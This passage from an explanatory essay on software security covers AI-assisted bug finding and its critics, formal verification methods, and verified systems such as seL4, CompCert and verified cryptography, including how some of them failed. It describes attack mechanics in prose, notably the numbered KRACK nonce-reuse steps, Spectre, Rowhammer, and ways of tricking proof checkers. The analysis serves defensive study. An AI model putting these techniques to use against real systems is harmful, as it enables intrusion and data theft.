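Most of these searches relied on a crash or a sanitizer report to confirm a flaw. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026), published on 2 December, tests how well language models find bugs without either. According to *Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (Pogorelec, 2026), the researchers gave Claude Mythos 5 unpatched code containing 21 known logic bugs, most of them in SQLite and an image library. A bug counted as found if the model supplied an input that made the patched and unpatched versions behave differently.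 In half of the trials, the researchers also told the model which rule the code broke.

| Method | Found from code alone | Found when told the rule |
|---|---|---|
| Code review by an agent | 11 | 20 |
| Informal correctness proofs | 8 | 21 |
| Fuzzing with a model's help | 0 | 1 |
| Symbolic execution driven by a model | 0 | 2 |

The two simplest methods, code review and informal proof, scored much higher than the other two. In code review, the model reads the program and tests whether suspected bugs are real. In an informal proof, it tries to argue that the code is correct, and a step that fails points to a possible bug. Both methods scored roughly twice as high with the rule, so much of the difficulty was working out what the program should do. The rule barely helped the other two methods. In the symbolic execution trial, the model spotted 13 bugs by reading the code, but the engine confirmed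 only two.

The study is small, and all its bugs show up as wrong output from a library. A missing ownership check on a server might be harder to find, because the rule may not be in the code. But the same team found new bugs in less tidy settings, including macOS, the Rust compiler and the part of Linux that checks small programs before running them in the kernel.

### The critics' case

Much of this evidence comes from a company that sells the models. Ottenheimer (2026), in *Claude Mythos & Project Glasswing*, objects that Anthropic published no steps for reproducing its findings, and that other people repeated its best-known ones with cheaper models. The security firm AISLE tried eight freely downloadable models, and all of them detected a flaw in the operating system FreeBSD that Anthropic had publicised. Niels Provos, whose code contained the OpenBSD flaw featured at the launch, found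 it again with public models and also found new flaws in other software. These results are good evidence that models other than Mythos can do such work, but weaker evidence that cheap models are equally good at searching, because people repeating a find already know there is something to look for. The repeats also make it harder to argue that the flaws are imaginary.

Ottenheimer also says the FreeBSD find was recall rather than discovery. MIT had fixed the shared code in 2007, FreeBSD imported an unfixed copy a year later, and the fix was in the model's training data. Recall may well explain this find, although FreeBSD's users were still exposed. It is a less convincing explanation for hundreds of Firefox bugs that nobody had fixed.

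A related complaint is that the tests leave out a product's usual defences. Mozilla's sandbox tests assume that the attacker already controls the sandboxed process, and they let the model rewrite the code that runs there. Mozilla replies that its bug bounty has similar rules, since real attackers chain several flaws together. It also says that a single high-severity bug is usually not enough to compromise Firefox, so the 271 bugs should not be counted as 271 separate ways to compromise it. Anthropic answered the complaint more directly in October with *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026), which describes five complete attacks by an unreleased model, including one that runs an attacker's code in Chrome after a single click. These attacks are strong evidence about that model, but weaker evidence about the claims made for Mythos Preview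 in April.

The false-alarm rate is still in dispute. Schneier on Security's *Mythos and Cybersecurity* argues that without the rate for the model's unfiltered output, nobody can tell whether the publicised finds are typical. The rates in the table cover only about a sixth of the candidates. Results were much worse for the data-transfer tool curl, whose maintainers received reports that no person at Anthropic had reviewed. Stenberg's *curl on OSS-Scanner* (2026) describes a single email containing 45 reports, 44 of them rated low. According to VulnCheck's *After 7-months, Glasswing Overwelms Maintainers with Underwhelming Findings* (2026), the maintainers had judged 25 by early November. They decided that 19 were not vulnerabilities and confirmed six, all of low severity.

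VulnCheck's main criticism is that Anthropic's public ledger lists only 217 of 37,966 findings as fixed. That comparison is unfair because most of the findings had never been reported to a maintainer. Of the 5,087 that had been, 629 had patches by late November, or about 12%. That rate is still low, and it is hard to check because Anthropic's ledger and dashboard give different counts. Anthropic attributes the low rate to the time patches take, unannounced fixes and overloaded maintainers.

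VulnCheck also points out that attackers have used only two of the 442 CVEs (entries in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities) that it credits to Anthropic. But defenders hope to fix flaws before attackers use them, so a low number could mean that the project is working. CVE counts are also a poor measure of how many bugs were found, because one entry can cover many bugs. Mozilla groups its internal finds, and three entries for Firefox 150 cover 316 bugs, so Ottenheimer's reduction of Mozilla's 271 bugs to "roughly three" doesn't show that Mozilla found few bugs.

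### What a search that finds nothing is worth

Suppose a fuzzer tries n inputs, each with the same independent chance p of exposing a flaw. The chance of seeing no failure is (1 − p)ⁿ, which drops below 5% once p exceeds about 3/n. Five million clean runs would be good evidence that fewer than about six in ten million inputs expose a flaw. Real fuzzers do not draw inputs independently, so this figure is optimistic. The calculation also assumes that somebody would notice the failure, which was not true of Heartbleed.

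Code that passes review by one model may also contain bugs that a later model can find. In the logic-bug study, code review found one of the 21 bugs with Claude Sonnet 4.5, five with Claude Opus 4.5 and 15 with Claude Mythos 5.2, which still missed six. A team that fixed everything Sonnet 4.5 found would have been left with 20 bugs.

Defenders can measure how well a search works by planting flaws of their own, as DARPA did. A search that misses a quarter of the planted flaws has probably missed some real ones too, and real flaws may be harder to find than the ones defenders think to plant. If separate searches find mostly the same flaws, there may be few findable flaws left. Anthropic's *Updating our coordinated vulnerability disclosure policy timelines* (2026) reports that different searchers increasingly find the same flaws, and gives this as a reason for cutting the time Anthropic allows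 for fixing serious flaws from 90 days to 30, starting in January 2027.

If a defender's search finds nothing, an attacker with similar tools and a similar budget will probably find little as well. The result gives much less assurance against an attacker who has a better model or who exploits a rule that nobody thought to check.

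## How is software proved secure, and where has that been done?

A proof has to cover every run of a program, including those that a search for bugs doesn't try, and a program with loops can have too many runs to list. In the late 1960s, Robert Floyd and Tony Hoare showed how to turn a claim about every run into a short list of logical statements that people or machines can check without running the program.

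### Preconditions, postconditions and invariants

In Hoare's method, each piece of code has a contract, made up of a precondition that must be true before the code runs and a postcondition that will be true when it finishes. The notation {P} C {Q} means that if P holds and the code C runs to its end, then Q holds. Whoever calls the code must make sure that P holds, and can then rely on Q without reading C. In the file reader, the allocator's postcondition is that the buffer has `size` bytes. The precondition for writing item i is that 8i + 8 is at most `size`.

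A tool can work through code without loops by itself. For a loop it also needs a loop invariant, which the engineer usually supplies. Here is the repaired file reader after the marker check, with an invariant strong enough to prove memory safety:

```
read n
stop if n > 536,870,911
size = 8 * n
buffer = allocate(size)
i = 0
while i < n:       invariant: i ≤ n, and size is exactly 8 × n
    read the next 8-byte item
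    write it to the buffer at position 8 * i
    i = i + 1
```

From the contracts and the invariant, the tool generates verification conditions, which are logical statements that together imply that the program meets its specification. This program has three, which put the earlier informal proof into a form that a tool can check:

1. Before the loop, i is 0, so i ≤ n, and the limit on n ensures that size is exactly 8 × n.
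2. At the write, the invariant holds and i < n. So i ≤ n − 1, which gives 8i + 8 ≤ 8 × n = size.
3. At the end of a pass, i has grown by 1. It was less than n before, so it is at most n now, and the loop has not changed n or size.

To check the second condition, the tool uses the solver to search for values where size = 8 × n and i < n but 8i + 8 is greater than size, and the solver finds none. Showing that all three conditions hold completes the proof. None of them depends on how many times the loop has already run, so three checks cover a loop that can run 536,870,911 times.

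Choosing the invariant takes most of the skill. Without the part about size, the second condition would fail for values such as i = 100 and size = 40, the same impossible combination that caused the false alarm in interval analysis. If the engineer had written i < n instead of i ≤ n, the third condition would fail on the last pass, when i reaches n.

A failed proof doesn't show that the program is wrong. The makers of Dafny, a programming language with a built-in verifier that uses Z3, give three possible causes: a mistake in the specification, a mistake in the code, or a missing annotation. Their example program finds the whole-number square root of N by counting r up from 0 while (r + 1)² ≤ N. The postcondition is r² ≤ N < (r + 1)². The second half holds because the loop stops only when (r + 1)² exceeds N, but Dafny cannot prove the first half until the programmer adds r² ≤ N as a loop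 invariant.

A program that never finishes satisfies {P} C {Q} for any Q, so engineers also have to prove that the loop ends. They do this by showing that some whole number decreases on every pass and cannot go below zero. In the file reader, that number is n − i. Solvers handle simple arithmetic like this well, but they often fail on conditions about linked data structures or products of unknowns, so engineers prove those in a proof assistant.

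### Refinement

A large system has thousands of functions, and a reader could hardly tell what the system does from their separate contracts. So engineers often write an abstract model of the whole system and prove that the code refines it.

A model of the file reader could be a list that starts empty and gains one item at a time. The real program has a buffer and a counter i instead. To connect them, the engineer defines the program and the model as matching when the first 8i bytes of the buffer encode exactly the items in the list. The engineer then proves that they match at the start, and that whenever they match and the program takes a step, the model can take a step or stay where it is so that they match again. Every run of the program therefore matches some run of the model, so if the items are always in the right order in the model, they are in the right order in the program too.

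Engineers can prevent leaks like the key in a reply's spare bytes by writing a model that leaves no such choices open. If the model requires the spare bytes to be zero, a program that puts the key there does not refine the model.

### Noninterference

If obs(x, k) is what an observer sees when the program runs with public input x and secret k, noninterference means that obs(x, k₁) = obs(x, k₂) for every x and every pair of secrets k₁ and k₂. To prove this, engineers reason about two runs side by side, using the invariant that everything the observer could see has the same value in both.

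Suppose the server runs the file reader twice on the same file with different encryption keys. The marker, the count and the items are the same in both runs. Each step computes new values only from values that are already the same, so the replies are the same too. This kind of proof would have failed for Heartbleed at the step that copied the message, because that step also copied bytes beyond the end of the message, which could differ between the two runs.

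Most systems have to let some information out. For example, an encryption component reads secret messages from a mail program and sends encrypted versions to the network. Intransitive noninterference allows this with a policy that lists which components may pass information directly to which others. The mail program may then pass secrets to the encryption component, but not directly to the network.

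### The seL4 microkernel

The best-known verified system is seL4, a microkernel, which is a small operating-system core with full control of the processor. It isolates the programs running on it from one another and leaves files, networking and most device drivers to them. A team in Australia finished the main proof on 29 July 2009. Kleppmann says the kernel has 8,700 lines of C and the proof took 200,000 lines of Isabelle and 20 person-years. Heiser (2026), in *seL4*, gives 11 person-years, which excludes the work on frameworks that other projects can reuse.

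The main theorem is functional correctness, which means that the C code refines the kernel's specification. As seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* explains, this also rules out buffer overflows, null pointer errors and several other kinds of bug. Further proofs show that the kernel can enforce three security properties:

- Integrity: a program cannot change data without permission.
- Availability: a program cannot interfere with another program's access to resources.
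- Confidentiality: a program cannot learn another program's information without permission.

seL4 represents permissions as capabilities, each of which combines a reference to an object with a set of rights over it. *Formally Verified Software in the Real World* gives an example in which component A's only right over anything else is to send messages to component B. A can therefore change only itself, B's message buffer and the state of B's thread. The seL4 team also proved a confidentiality property called intransitive noninterference. Their 2013 slides from NICTA, the Australian research centre where they worked, describe this as the first such theorem for a general-purpose kernel. The slides also note that the theorem does not cover timing channels, so a program might still learn something about another by measuring how long operations take.

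The proofs cover some versions of the kernel more fully than others. In 2026 the verification company Proofcraft finished the confidentiality proof for AArch64, the 64-bit Arm architecture used in most phones. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 News* reports that this completes the security proofs for the C code on that architecture. On ARMv7 and 64-bit RISC-V, researchers have also proved that the compiler's output matches the C code, according to Trustworthy Systems' *The seL4 verification project*. AArch64 is not on that list, so its users still have to trust the compiler. In 2026 Proofcraft also proved functional correctness for a version that shares processor time between critical and less critical tasks, but so far only on RISC-V. The multicore version remains unverified.

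All of seL4's proofs assume that certain parts of the system work correctly. The seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume* lists about 340 lines of assembly code on Arm, about 1,200 lines of code that starts the kernel, and the hardware itself. The proofs also assume that no device overwrites the kernel's memory directly, so each device with direct memory access needs either a verified driver or a hardware unit that restricts its access.

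The seL4 Foundation says nobody has found a functional correctness defect in the kernel's verified code in more than 15 years of testing and use. The foundation promotes seL4, but it also reports defects in the unverified versions and in every kind of unverified code in the kernel. Mostly the same people wrote the verified and unverified code, so the proofs probably account for much of the difference. But the unverified parts include low-level code that is unusually hard to get right, so the comparison is not entirely fair.

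The kernel is now in commercial use. Heiser lists its use in national security systems, a system for voice communication between aircraft and the ground, and electric cars from the Chinese manufacturer NIO, starting with the ONVO L60 in 2024.

### HACMS and the helicopter

A verified kernel is most useful if it can protect a system that also contains unverified code. DARPA tested this in its High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems programme (HACMS), using a small quadcopter and Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a 32-foot autonomous helicopter. At the start of the programme, a red team of professional penetration testers broke into the helicopter's software within an hour and could have crashed the aircraft or sent it anywhere (Cofer, Gacek and colleagues, 2018, *A Formal Approach to Constructing Secure Air Vehicle Software*).

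The helicopter has one computer for flying and another, the mission computer, for communicating with the ground. Boeing's engineers put the seL4 kernel on the mission computer and moved the camera software, which they did not trust, into a virtual machine running Linux. The kernel restricted the camera software to a few narrow channels for reaching the rest of the aircraft. The engineers also rewrote the critical communication code in Ivory, a language designed to guarantee memory safety.

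The red team assessed the vehicles again after each of three 18-month phases. Its members had the design documents, source code, compiled programs and analysis results, and they attended design meetings, according to Fisher in *DARPA's HACMS Program*. For one test, they received root access (full control) inside the camera's virtual machine, but they could not escape it or disrupt the aircraft. During a flight in February 2017, with a safety pilot on board, the helicopter came under attack from its own camera software and from a virus on a USB stick. Some subsystems failed, but the helicopter kept flying safely.

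In its final report, the red team found no memory corruption, arithmetic faults or isolation failures in the verified components it assessed. At DEF CON in 2021, DARPA invited visitors to try to take over a drone protected by seL4, and Heiser reports that none succeeded.

These are test results, and nobody proved the whole aircraft secure. The helicopter's flight computer ran VxWorks, a commercial operating system without such proofs, and the engineers relied on the mission computer to shield it. They also excluded radio jamming and assumed that anyone with an authorised user's credentials could do anything. The redesign changed the architecture, the programming language and the kernel together, so the results do not show how much each contributed. The root-access test is the best evidence for the kernel, because the attackers began with full control of a neighbouring component and only the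 kernel's isolation could stop them.

According to DARPA (2025), the programme's tools are publicly available, and parts of the US government and of the defence and commercial sectors have adopted them.

### CompCert and the search for compiler bugs

A proof about C code can fail to hold for the running program if the compiler makes a mistake. Leroy, in *Formal verification of a realistic compiler*, describes CompCert, a C compiler with a proof in Rocq (then called Coq). The theorem says that if a source program S can never do anything undefined, every behaviour of the compiled program C is also a behaviour of S:

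```
S is safe  ⟹  for every behaviour B, if C can do B then S can do B
```

A program's behaviour here includes its inputs, its outputs and whether it finishes. CompCert translates a program in 14 passes, and Leroy proved refinement for each pass separately.

One compiler pass decides which values to keep in the processor's few registers. The method for choosing a good arrangement is hard to prove correct, so Leroy left it unverified and proved a small checker correct instead. The checker confirms that two values never share a register while the program still needs both. If the check fails, the compiler stops, so a mistake in the unverified part can prevent a program from compiling but cannot make the compiler produce incorrect code.

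The theorem does not help much if the source program already has a flaw. Writing outside a buffer is undefined in C, so the original file reader is not safe in the theorem's sense, and the theorem guarantees nothing about its compiled version.

*Finding and Understanding Bugs in C Compilers* (Yang, Chen and colleagues, 2011) provided independent evidence. It describes Csmith, a tool that generates random C programs that each have only one correct result. The researchers compiled each program with several compilers, ran the compiled versions and compared the results. Over three years they reported more than 325 bugs to the teams behind 11 compilers, including GCC and LLVM. Every compiler they tested crashed on some valid programs and compiled others incorrectly without warning.

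CompCert was one of the 11, but its translation errors came from outside the proof. Six were in an unverified part that ran before the verified passes. One of these made the compiler treat −1 as a huge positive number in a comparison. Two more arose because Leroy's model of the PowerPC processor left out a limit on the size of a number in an instruction. The assembler, a separate program that runs afterwards, rejected the resulting instructions.

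Yang and colleagues then spent about six years of processor time testing a newer version of CompCert and found no translation errors. They had found bugs in the optimising passes of all the other compilers they tested, but none in CompCert's. This is unusually good evidence that a proof made a practical difference, because they used the same tool to search all the compilers for the same kind of mistake.

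CompCert is a commercial product, mainly for safety-critical embedded software. In Leroy's early tests, programs compiled with CompCert ran 12% slower on average than those compiled with GCC using its usual optimisations.

### Cryptography

Cryptographic code has been formally verified more than most other software in everyday use. An arithmetic error may affect so few inputs that testing misses it, but an attacker who identifies those inputs may be able to recover a key. The main verification projects have proved different properties of this code.

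| Project | What the proofs establish | Where it is in use |
|---|---|---|
| HACL* and EverCrypt | The code computes the standard algorithms, is memory-safe, and never branches on a secret or uses one as a memory address | Code from these libraries is in Firefox, the Linux kernel and Python |
| Amazon's s2n | The code for message authentication, random numbers and the order of handshake messages matches its specifications | Amazon services, including S3 storage |
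| Analyses of TLS 1.3 | In a model of the protocol, attackers cannot learn the session keys or impersonate the parties, under stated assumptions | Browsers and websites use the protocol, but the proofs do not cover their code |
| Apple's corecrypto | The code for two quantum-resistant algorithms matches the official standards | Apple's operating systems |

HACL*'s developers write the library in F*, a language that supports proofs, and then translate it into C. EverCrypt adds verified assembly code and selects the fastest version for each processor. The rule about secrets is a form of noninterference. It assumes an observer can see which instructions run and which memory addresses they use, and it requires that secrets affect neither. This removes the most common timing leaks, but not those from instructions that take longer on some values.

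Amazon set up s2n's proofs to rerun automatically whenever the code changes. Otherwise, a proof can become outdated as soon as a programmer fixes a bug or adds a feature.

TLS is the protocol that encrypts web traffic. Researchers found many of the attacks on earlier versions only after websites were using those versions, but they analyzed TLS 1.3 while it was still being drafted. *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* notes that formal verification helped to find an attack on one draft that let an adversary impersonate a client. The designers could then fix the flaw before publishing the standard in 2018. Verifying a protocol's design does not prevent mistakes in the programs that implement it, such as Heartbleed.

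*A blueprint for formal verification of Apple corecrypto* (2026) gives the most detailed recent account of a software verification project. The corecrypto library runs on over 2.5 billion active devices. Apple verified its implementations of two algorithms that NIST had standardized: ML-KEM, which lets two parties agree on a secret key, and ML-DSA, which produces digital signatures.

Apple's engineers rewrote their C code by hand in Cryptol, a language for describing algorithms, and used a tool called SAW to check that the two versions matched. Another tool translated the Cryptol version into Isabelle. The engineers also wrote the NIST standards in Isabelle by hand and proved that the translated version agreed with them, which took more than 50,000 proof steps. They also proved that each hand-optimised assembly routine gave the same results as the C routine it replaced.

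Proving each routine separately was not enough, because one routine could produce a number outside the range that the next one accepted. The work exposed such a flaw in an early version of the ML-DSA code, where a missing step let numbers go out of range in rare cases and produce wrong results. Apple says its existing tests would not have caught the flaw, which it fixed before release.

The proofs assume that the C compiler is correct. Because of a limit in SAW, they could not cover every message length for ML-DSA, so Apple tested that part conventionally. Apple also relied on testing to look for information leaks. The proofs do not show that the algorithms themselves are hard to break, so a mathematical attack on ML-KEM would work even against a perfect implementation.

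### Why most software went without proofs

Kernels, compilers and cryptographic routines are unusually good candidates for proof because their verified parts are small and their specifications are short compared with those of most applications and change slowly. A NIST standard defines exactly what a cryptographic algorithm should compute, and a compiler's specification comes from the definitions of its source and target languages. A web browser has no comparable description, and its features change every few weeks. Reuse also matters. Heiser writes that the effort behind seL4 makes sense only for something that many systems will use.

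Kleppmann calculates that seL4 needed 23 lines of proof and half a person-day for every line of code, and guesses that only a few hundred people in the world could write such proofs. Leroy's figures imply that CompCert needed only about five lines of proof per line of compiler, partly because he wrote the compiler in Rocq's own language and could reason about it directly. It had still taken about three person-years by 2009. Kleppmann also suggests that much of the harm from bugs falls on users rather than developers, which gives developers even less reason to pay for proofs.

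Proofs look less expensive for software that already has to meet strict standards. Heiser says that seL4's proof cost no more than the usual methods for high-assurance software, which give no guarantee. Very little software is developed with those methods, so the comparison makes no difference to most developers.

The effort needed to prove a program secure grows faster than the program's size. Heiser cites research showing that the effort grows with the square of the specification's size, and *How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?* assumes that this also holds for code size. On that assumption, a program of 100,000 lines, ten times the size of seL4, would take 100 times the effort, or 2,000 person-years. Linux, with about 40 million lines, would take 128 million person-years, even if a team could repeat the seL4 proof in eight person-years. These figures rest on a few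 projects, so the Linux number in particular is only an illustration. But even if it were a thousand times too high, the proof would still take more work than anyone would have paid for.

Dividing a program into parts reduces the effort of verifying it. If engineers could split the 100,000 lines into ten independent modules, each the size of seL4, the total would fall to 200 person-years. Heiser calls this kind of calculation highly optimistic, because engineers would also have to specify how the modules interact.

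LionsOS, an operating system that Heiser's group is building on seL4, is still based on this idea. Most of its components have fewer than 500 lines, and the kernel isolates them so that engineers can verify each one separately. One of its network drivers has 569 lines, whereas the Linux driver for the same hardware has 4,775. Heiser expects the verification of LionsOS to be complete in 2027.

Existing software is harder to divide, and it is also difficult to replace. miTLS, a verified implementation of TLS, took ten years to develop and has had little use. Programs written for OpenSSL would need rewriting to work with it, because the two libraries offer different functions.

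## How have systems with proofs still failed?

Systems with proofs have failed because of gaps in the specification, unverified code, faulty checking and hardware that did not match the model.

### The specification left something out: KRACK

The WPA2 protocol encrypts most Wi-Fi traffic. When a laptop joins a network, it and the access point exchange four messages to agree on a fresh session key. Researchers proved this four-way handshake secure in 2005, and nobody found a weakness in it for 14 years after its introduction. In 2017, Mathy Vanhoef and Frank Piessens broke it with an attack called KRACK, which Vanhoef explains in *Key Reinstallation Attacks*.

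The laptop encrypts each packet with the session key and a packet number, or nonce, which must never repeat under the same key. The key and nonce determine a stream of bytes s, which the laptop combines with the message using exclusive-or (⊕). If the laptop encrypts two messages, p₁ and p₂, with the same stream, an attacker can combine the results, p₁ ⊕ s and p₂ ⊕ s, to cancel s and get p₁ ⊕ p₂. An attacker who can guess one message can then read the other.

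KRACK makes the laptop repeat its nonces:

1. The access point sends message 3. The laptop replies with message 4, installs the key and sets the nonce to zero.
2. The attacker, relaying traffic between the two, blocks message 4.
3. The laptop starts sending encrypted packets, and the nonce goes up by one each time.
4. The access point has received no reply, so it sends message 3 again.
5. The laptop installs the same key again and resets the nonce to zero, so its next packets reuse the earlier nonces.

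The 2005 proof established that the session key stays private and that each side verifies the other's identity, and both remain true throughout the attack. But the proof did not model when a device installs the key, so it could not rule out a second installation.

Windows and iOS 10 resisted this version of the attack because they ignored repeats of message 3, which violated the standard. The attack was more severe against a common Linux client that Android also used. That client erased the key from memory after installing it, apparently because of a remark in the standard, so the second installation used an all-zero key.

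The first repairs came without proofs, and in 2018 Vanhoef and Piessens bypassed both their own countermeasures and a different one from the standards body, IEEE. In *A Formal Analysis of IEEE 802.11's WPA2* (2020), Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger built the first model detailed enough to show the attacks. Models of this kind usually assume perfect encryption, meaning that nobody can read a message without the key. Under that assumption, reusing a nonce does no harm, so the models could not reveal KRACK. Cremers, Kiesl and Medinger dropped the assumption and added features that had seemed irrelevant to security, such as a power-saving mode. Their model reproduced KRACK, and they proved that some of the later countermeasures stop it, but only after the attack had shown what the model needed to include.

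### Part of the system was unverified

*An Empirical Study on the Correctness of Formally Verified Distributed Systems* (Fonseca, Zhang and colleagues, 2017) examined IronFleet, Verdi and Chapar, three research systems that keep data consistent across several machines. All three had machine-checked proofs, but the researchers found 16 bugs through code review and testing.

| Where the bugs were | Number | Example |
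|---|---|---|
| Shim layer, which connects the proved code to the network and disk | 11 | A client could hide a second command inside a request to Verdi, after which other requests returned the wrong values. |
| Specification | 2 | IronFleet's specification did not require the system to carry out each request only once. |
| Verification tools | 3 | A signal from the operating system could make IronFleet's tools accept an incorrect program. |
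| The proved protocols | 0 | |

Many of the shim bugs arose because the code didn't meet the proof's assumptions. Chapar's algorithm, for example, required a reliable network, but its servers exchanged updates over UDP, which can lose or duplicate packets. A duplicate of an old update could overwrite a newer one.

The zero for protocol bugs is the most informative number in the table, because the researchers spent more than eight months on the study and looked specifically for such bugs. Many of the known bugs they checked in mature distributed systems without proofs were at the protocol level. Three prototypes are a small sample, but the contrast is hard to explain unless the proofs made a difference.

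A more recent case is lean-zip, a compression library that ten AI agents wrote and proved correct in Lean. One of its main theorems is that compressing any data under a gigabyte and then decompressing it returns the original. *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug*, a post on the blog To Proof Maintenance & Beyond!, describes an attempt to break it in April 2026. The blogger removed the theorems and documentation so that a Claude agent would not give up early, then gave the agent the code and a set of fuzzing tools. Sixteen fuzzers ran for about 19 hours and tried 105.8 million inputs. They found no memory errors in the compiled application code, but found two flaws elsewhere.

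The first bug was in the parser that reads ZIP archives, which no theorem covered. The parser read a file's compressed size from the archive's header and tried to allocate that much memory without checking whether the archive was that big. A 156-byte archive whose header listed a size in the exabytes crashed the program.

The second flaw was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that every compiled Lean program depends on. To hold n bytes, the runtime allocates 24 + n bytes, computing the sum in 64-bit arithmetic. If n is 2⁶⁴ − 1, the sum wraps round to 23, and the program reads a file into a 23-byte buffer. Like the file reader's flaw, this is an integer overflow, but in an addition rather than a multiplication. It affected every version of Lean 4 up to that point. A crafted archive could trigger it through the unverified parser, so a size check in the parser would have protected lean-zip from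 both flaws.

### The label promised more than the proof

Anyone could see that the lean-zip parser had no theorems, but the limits of a proof are sometimes harder to find. Cryspen maintains libcrux, a cryptographic library in Rust, and Signal has used some of its code. Symbolic Software's *On the Promises of 'High-Assurance' Cryptography* (2026) objects to Cryspen describing the library as "formally verified" and as offering "the highest level of assurance".

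*Verification Theatre* (Kobeissi, 2026) lists 13 flaws in libcrux and a related library, hpke-rs. Nine were in unverified code, including one that caused real decryption failures in Signal's software. In hpke-rs, a 32-bit message counter wrapped round to zero, so the library reused nonces, the mistake that KRACK exploits. The other four were in specifications and proofs. Kobeissi calls all 13 vulnerabilities, although an attacker can't exploit a wrong specification if the code is correct.

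Bhargavan (2026), Cryspen's chief research scientist, replied to the first findings on 12 February in *The strengths and limits of formal verification*. Bhargavan wrote that the guarantees cover only the verified modules, that the repository documents which modules those are, and that nobody had found a bug in the verified code. Kobeissi's firm, Symbolic Software, answered the same day in *We Found Bugs in CE Labs' Verified Code* (2026), which calls Cryspen "CE Labs".

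One of the post's examples concerns ML-KEM, the key-agreement algorithm that Apple also verified. ML-KEM shrinks numbers to d bits and later scales them back up as 3,329x / 2ᵈ, rounded to the nearest whole number. To round this way, a program adds half the divisor, 2ᵈ⁻¹, before dividing. The specification instead added 1,664, which is the right constant for the reverse operation. With d = 1, it turned 0 into 832. At d = 11, the two formulas agree on 1,408 of the 2,048 values, so the post overstates the error when it reports a wrong answer for every input at every size ML-KEM uses. The error had been in the specification since the first version.

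The Rust code used the correct constant but the specification did not, so no valid proof could connect them, and a full check would have exposed the mistake. But the build settings made the checker accept that module without proof. A second module contained a false lemma, that any number from 0 to 4,095 fits in a single bit. The build skipped that proof by default because it was slow, and no automated job in the repository turned it on. A status page nevertheless listed both modules as verified for correctness.

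Kobeissi's firm sells audits of cryptographic software and its posts are hostile, but these errors were in files that anyone could inspect. Bhargavan's statement is accurate if "verified code" means code whose proofs a checker has accepted in full, but not if it means the modules that the status page listed as verified, which is how a customer would probably read it. Bhargavan also writes that every change must pass verification again before it is merged, which is hard to reconcile with the build settings. Cryspen began revising its documentation that week, and in its *Security Policy* it promises security advisories for releases with bug fixes from February 2026 onwards.

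Kobeissi found the same types of failure in Amazon's verified cryptographic library. Amazon and Cryspen differed in how clearly they documented the limits of their proofs and whether they ran the proofs automatically.

### The tool accepted something false

A checker can also run and accept a contradiction, known as a proof of False. The step that translates code for the checker can cause this too. Cryspen uses a tool called hax to translate Rust into F*, the proof language behind HACL*. Symbolic Software's *The Verification Facade* (2026) presents five small programs that exploit gaps in this translation. One program, which prepares a secret key for the signature algorithm Ed25519, sets a bit of the key that it should clear. On the next line, the programmer uses a hax command to assume that the bit is clear. The command does nothing in Rust, but in F* it adds an axiom that contradicts the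 line above, so F* accepts any claim about the rest of the function. Ordinary tests also pass, because the key still produces valid signatures.

Another of the five programs rotates the bits of a number, as many ciphers do. The hax library's specification for F* states only that a rotation returns a 32-bit number, not which one, so a cipher that rotated by 15 places instead of 16 would also pass.

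Three of the five programs passed F*'s full check. They are demonstrations rather than deployed software, and in the Ed25519 example a programmer had to write the false assumption. According to the post, hax does verify simpler code, such as loops with a fixed range.

Errors in the checker seem to be rare. *The Trusted Computing Base of the CompCert Verified Compiler* (2022) reports that none of CompCert's known problems were in its verified parts. It also considers it unlikely that someone would hit a checker bug by accident, notice nothing wrong and believe a false theorem. That reasoning works well for people who understand the theorem they are proving, but less well for an automated prover that tries one thing after another until the checker accepts, because its search could find a checker bug without anyone intending it.

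### The hardware did not match the model

Proofs about software usually assume that the processor runs instructions one after another and that memory keeps what the program wrote there. Two hardware attacks break these assumptions.

Spectre, an attack made public in 2018, exploits the way processors predict which branch a program will take and start executing it before the condition has been checked. If the prediction is wrong, the processor discards the results. But any data it loaded stays in the cache, a small fast memory, and an attacker can find out what is there by timing later reads. Suppose a server returns item i of a file only if i is less than n. After many valid requests, the processor predicts that the check will succeed. If the attacker then asks for a much larger i, the processor may briefly read far beyond the buffer that holds the file. The program as written never reads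 there, so a proof of its memory safety remains valid.

*Guarantees in Security* (Böhme, 2024) cites Spectre as a violation of the confidentiality guarantee that the seL4 team had proved. This is slightly overstated, because the team had already said that the theorem did not cover timing channels. The theorem still holds, but it covers less than most people would expect from the word "confidentiality". Extending it to timing channels is difficult because each processor optimisation needs its own rule. One rule might forbid speculation on branches that depend on a secret, and another might require cache misses to be independent of secrets. The next generation of processors could require more rules.

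Rowhammer is an attack on memory chips in which a program accesses the same rows of memory over and over to flip bits in neighbouring rows that it has no permission to change. Suppose the repaired file reader has accepted a file of three items and allocated 24 bytes. Flipping one high bit of n can then change it from 3 to 536,870,915, which makes the loop write past the end of the buffer. The proof assumed that n would stay the same during the loop because the code doesn't change it, but Rowhammer can change it in the memory chip.

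### Should people assume that flaws remain?

Böhme argues that people must generally assume that any sufficiently large software system contains exploitable flaws, even if it comes with credible assurances. The argument rests on nine obstacles to a reliable guarantee. Some concern the security requirements, which people may fail to foresee or define precisely. Others concern the reasoning, which depends on assumptions, leaves out detail and runs into limits such as Rice's theorem. The rest are social. For example, every check relies on another tool or person, and a system can look secure because nobody has had a reason to attack it.

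Böhme gives cases where each obstacle undermined a real system or a claim about one. In one of the strongest, Bognar and colleagues studied two processor designs for protecting sensitive code, both with security proofs. They identified nine assumptions behind the proofs and showed how to exploit every one. Böhme proposes continuing to look for attacks that succeed despite a defence, and using each one to repair both the system and the method that missed it, rather than dismissing proofs as useless. This is roughly what happened with WPA2.

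The examples show that no method rules out every attack, but showing that every large system has an exploitable flaw would require evidence about each system. "Must assume" makes more sense as sound advice about where the burden of proof lies.

The proved parts of these systems have mostly held up. KRACK never revealed the session key, and the searches of lean-zip and the three distributed systems found nothing wrong in the proved parts. There are exceptions. Böhme cites work by Kang and colleagues that found a false axiom in CompCert's proof, which could lead to a compiled program that calculated the wrong result.

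The defence that the proved part held can be empty, because after any failure someone can redraw the boundary of what was proved to exclude the flaw. Comparisons that don't depend on that boundary are better evidence of whether verification helps. Fonseca and colleagues compared verified systems with unverified ones. The Csmith tests did the same for compilers, and the results favoured CompCert, the verified compiler.

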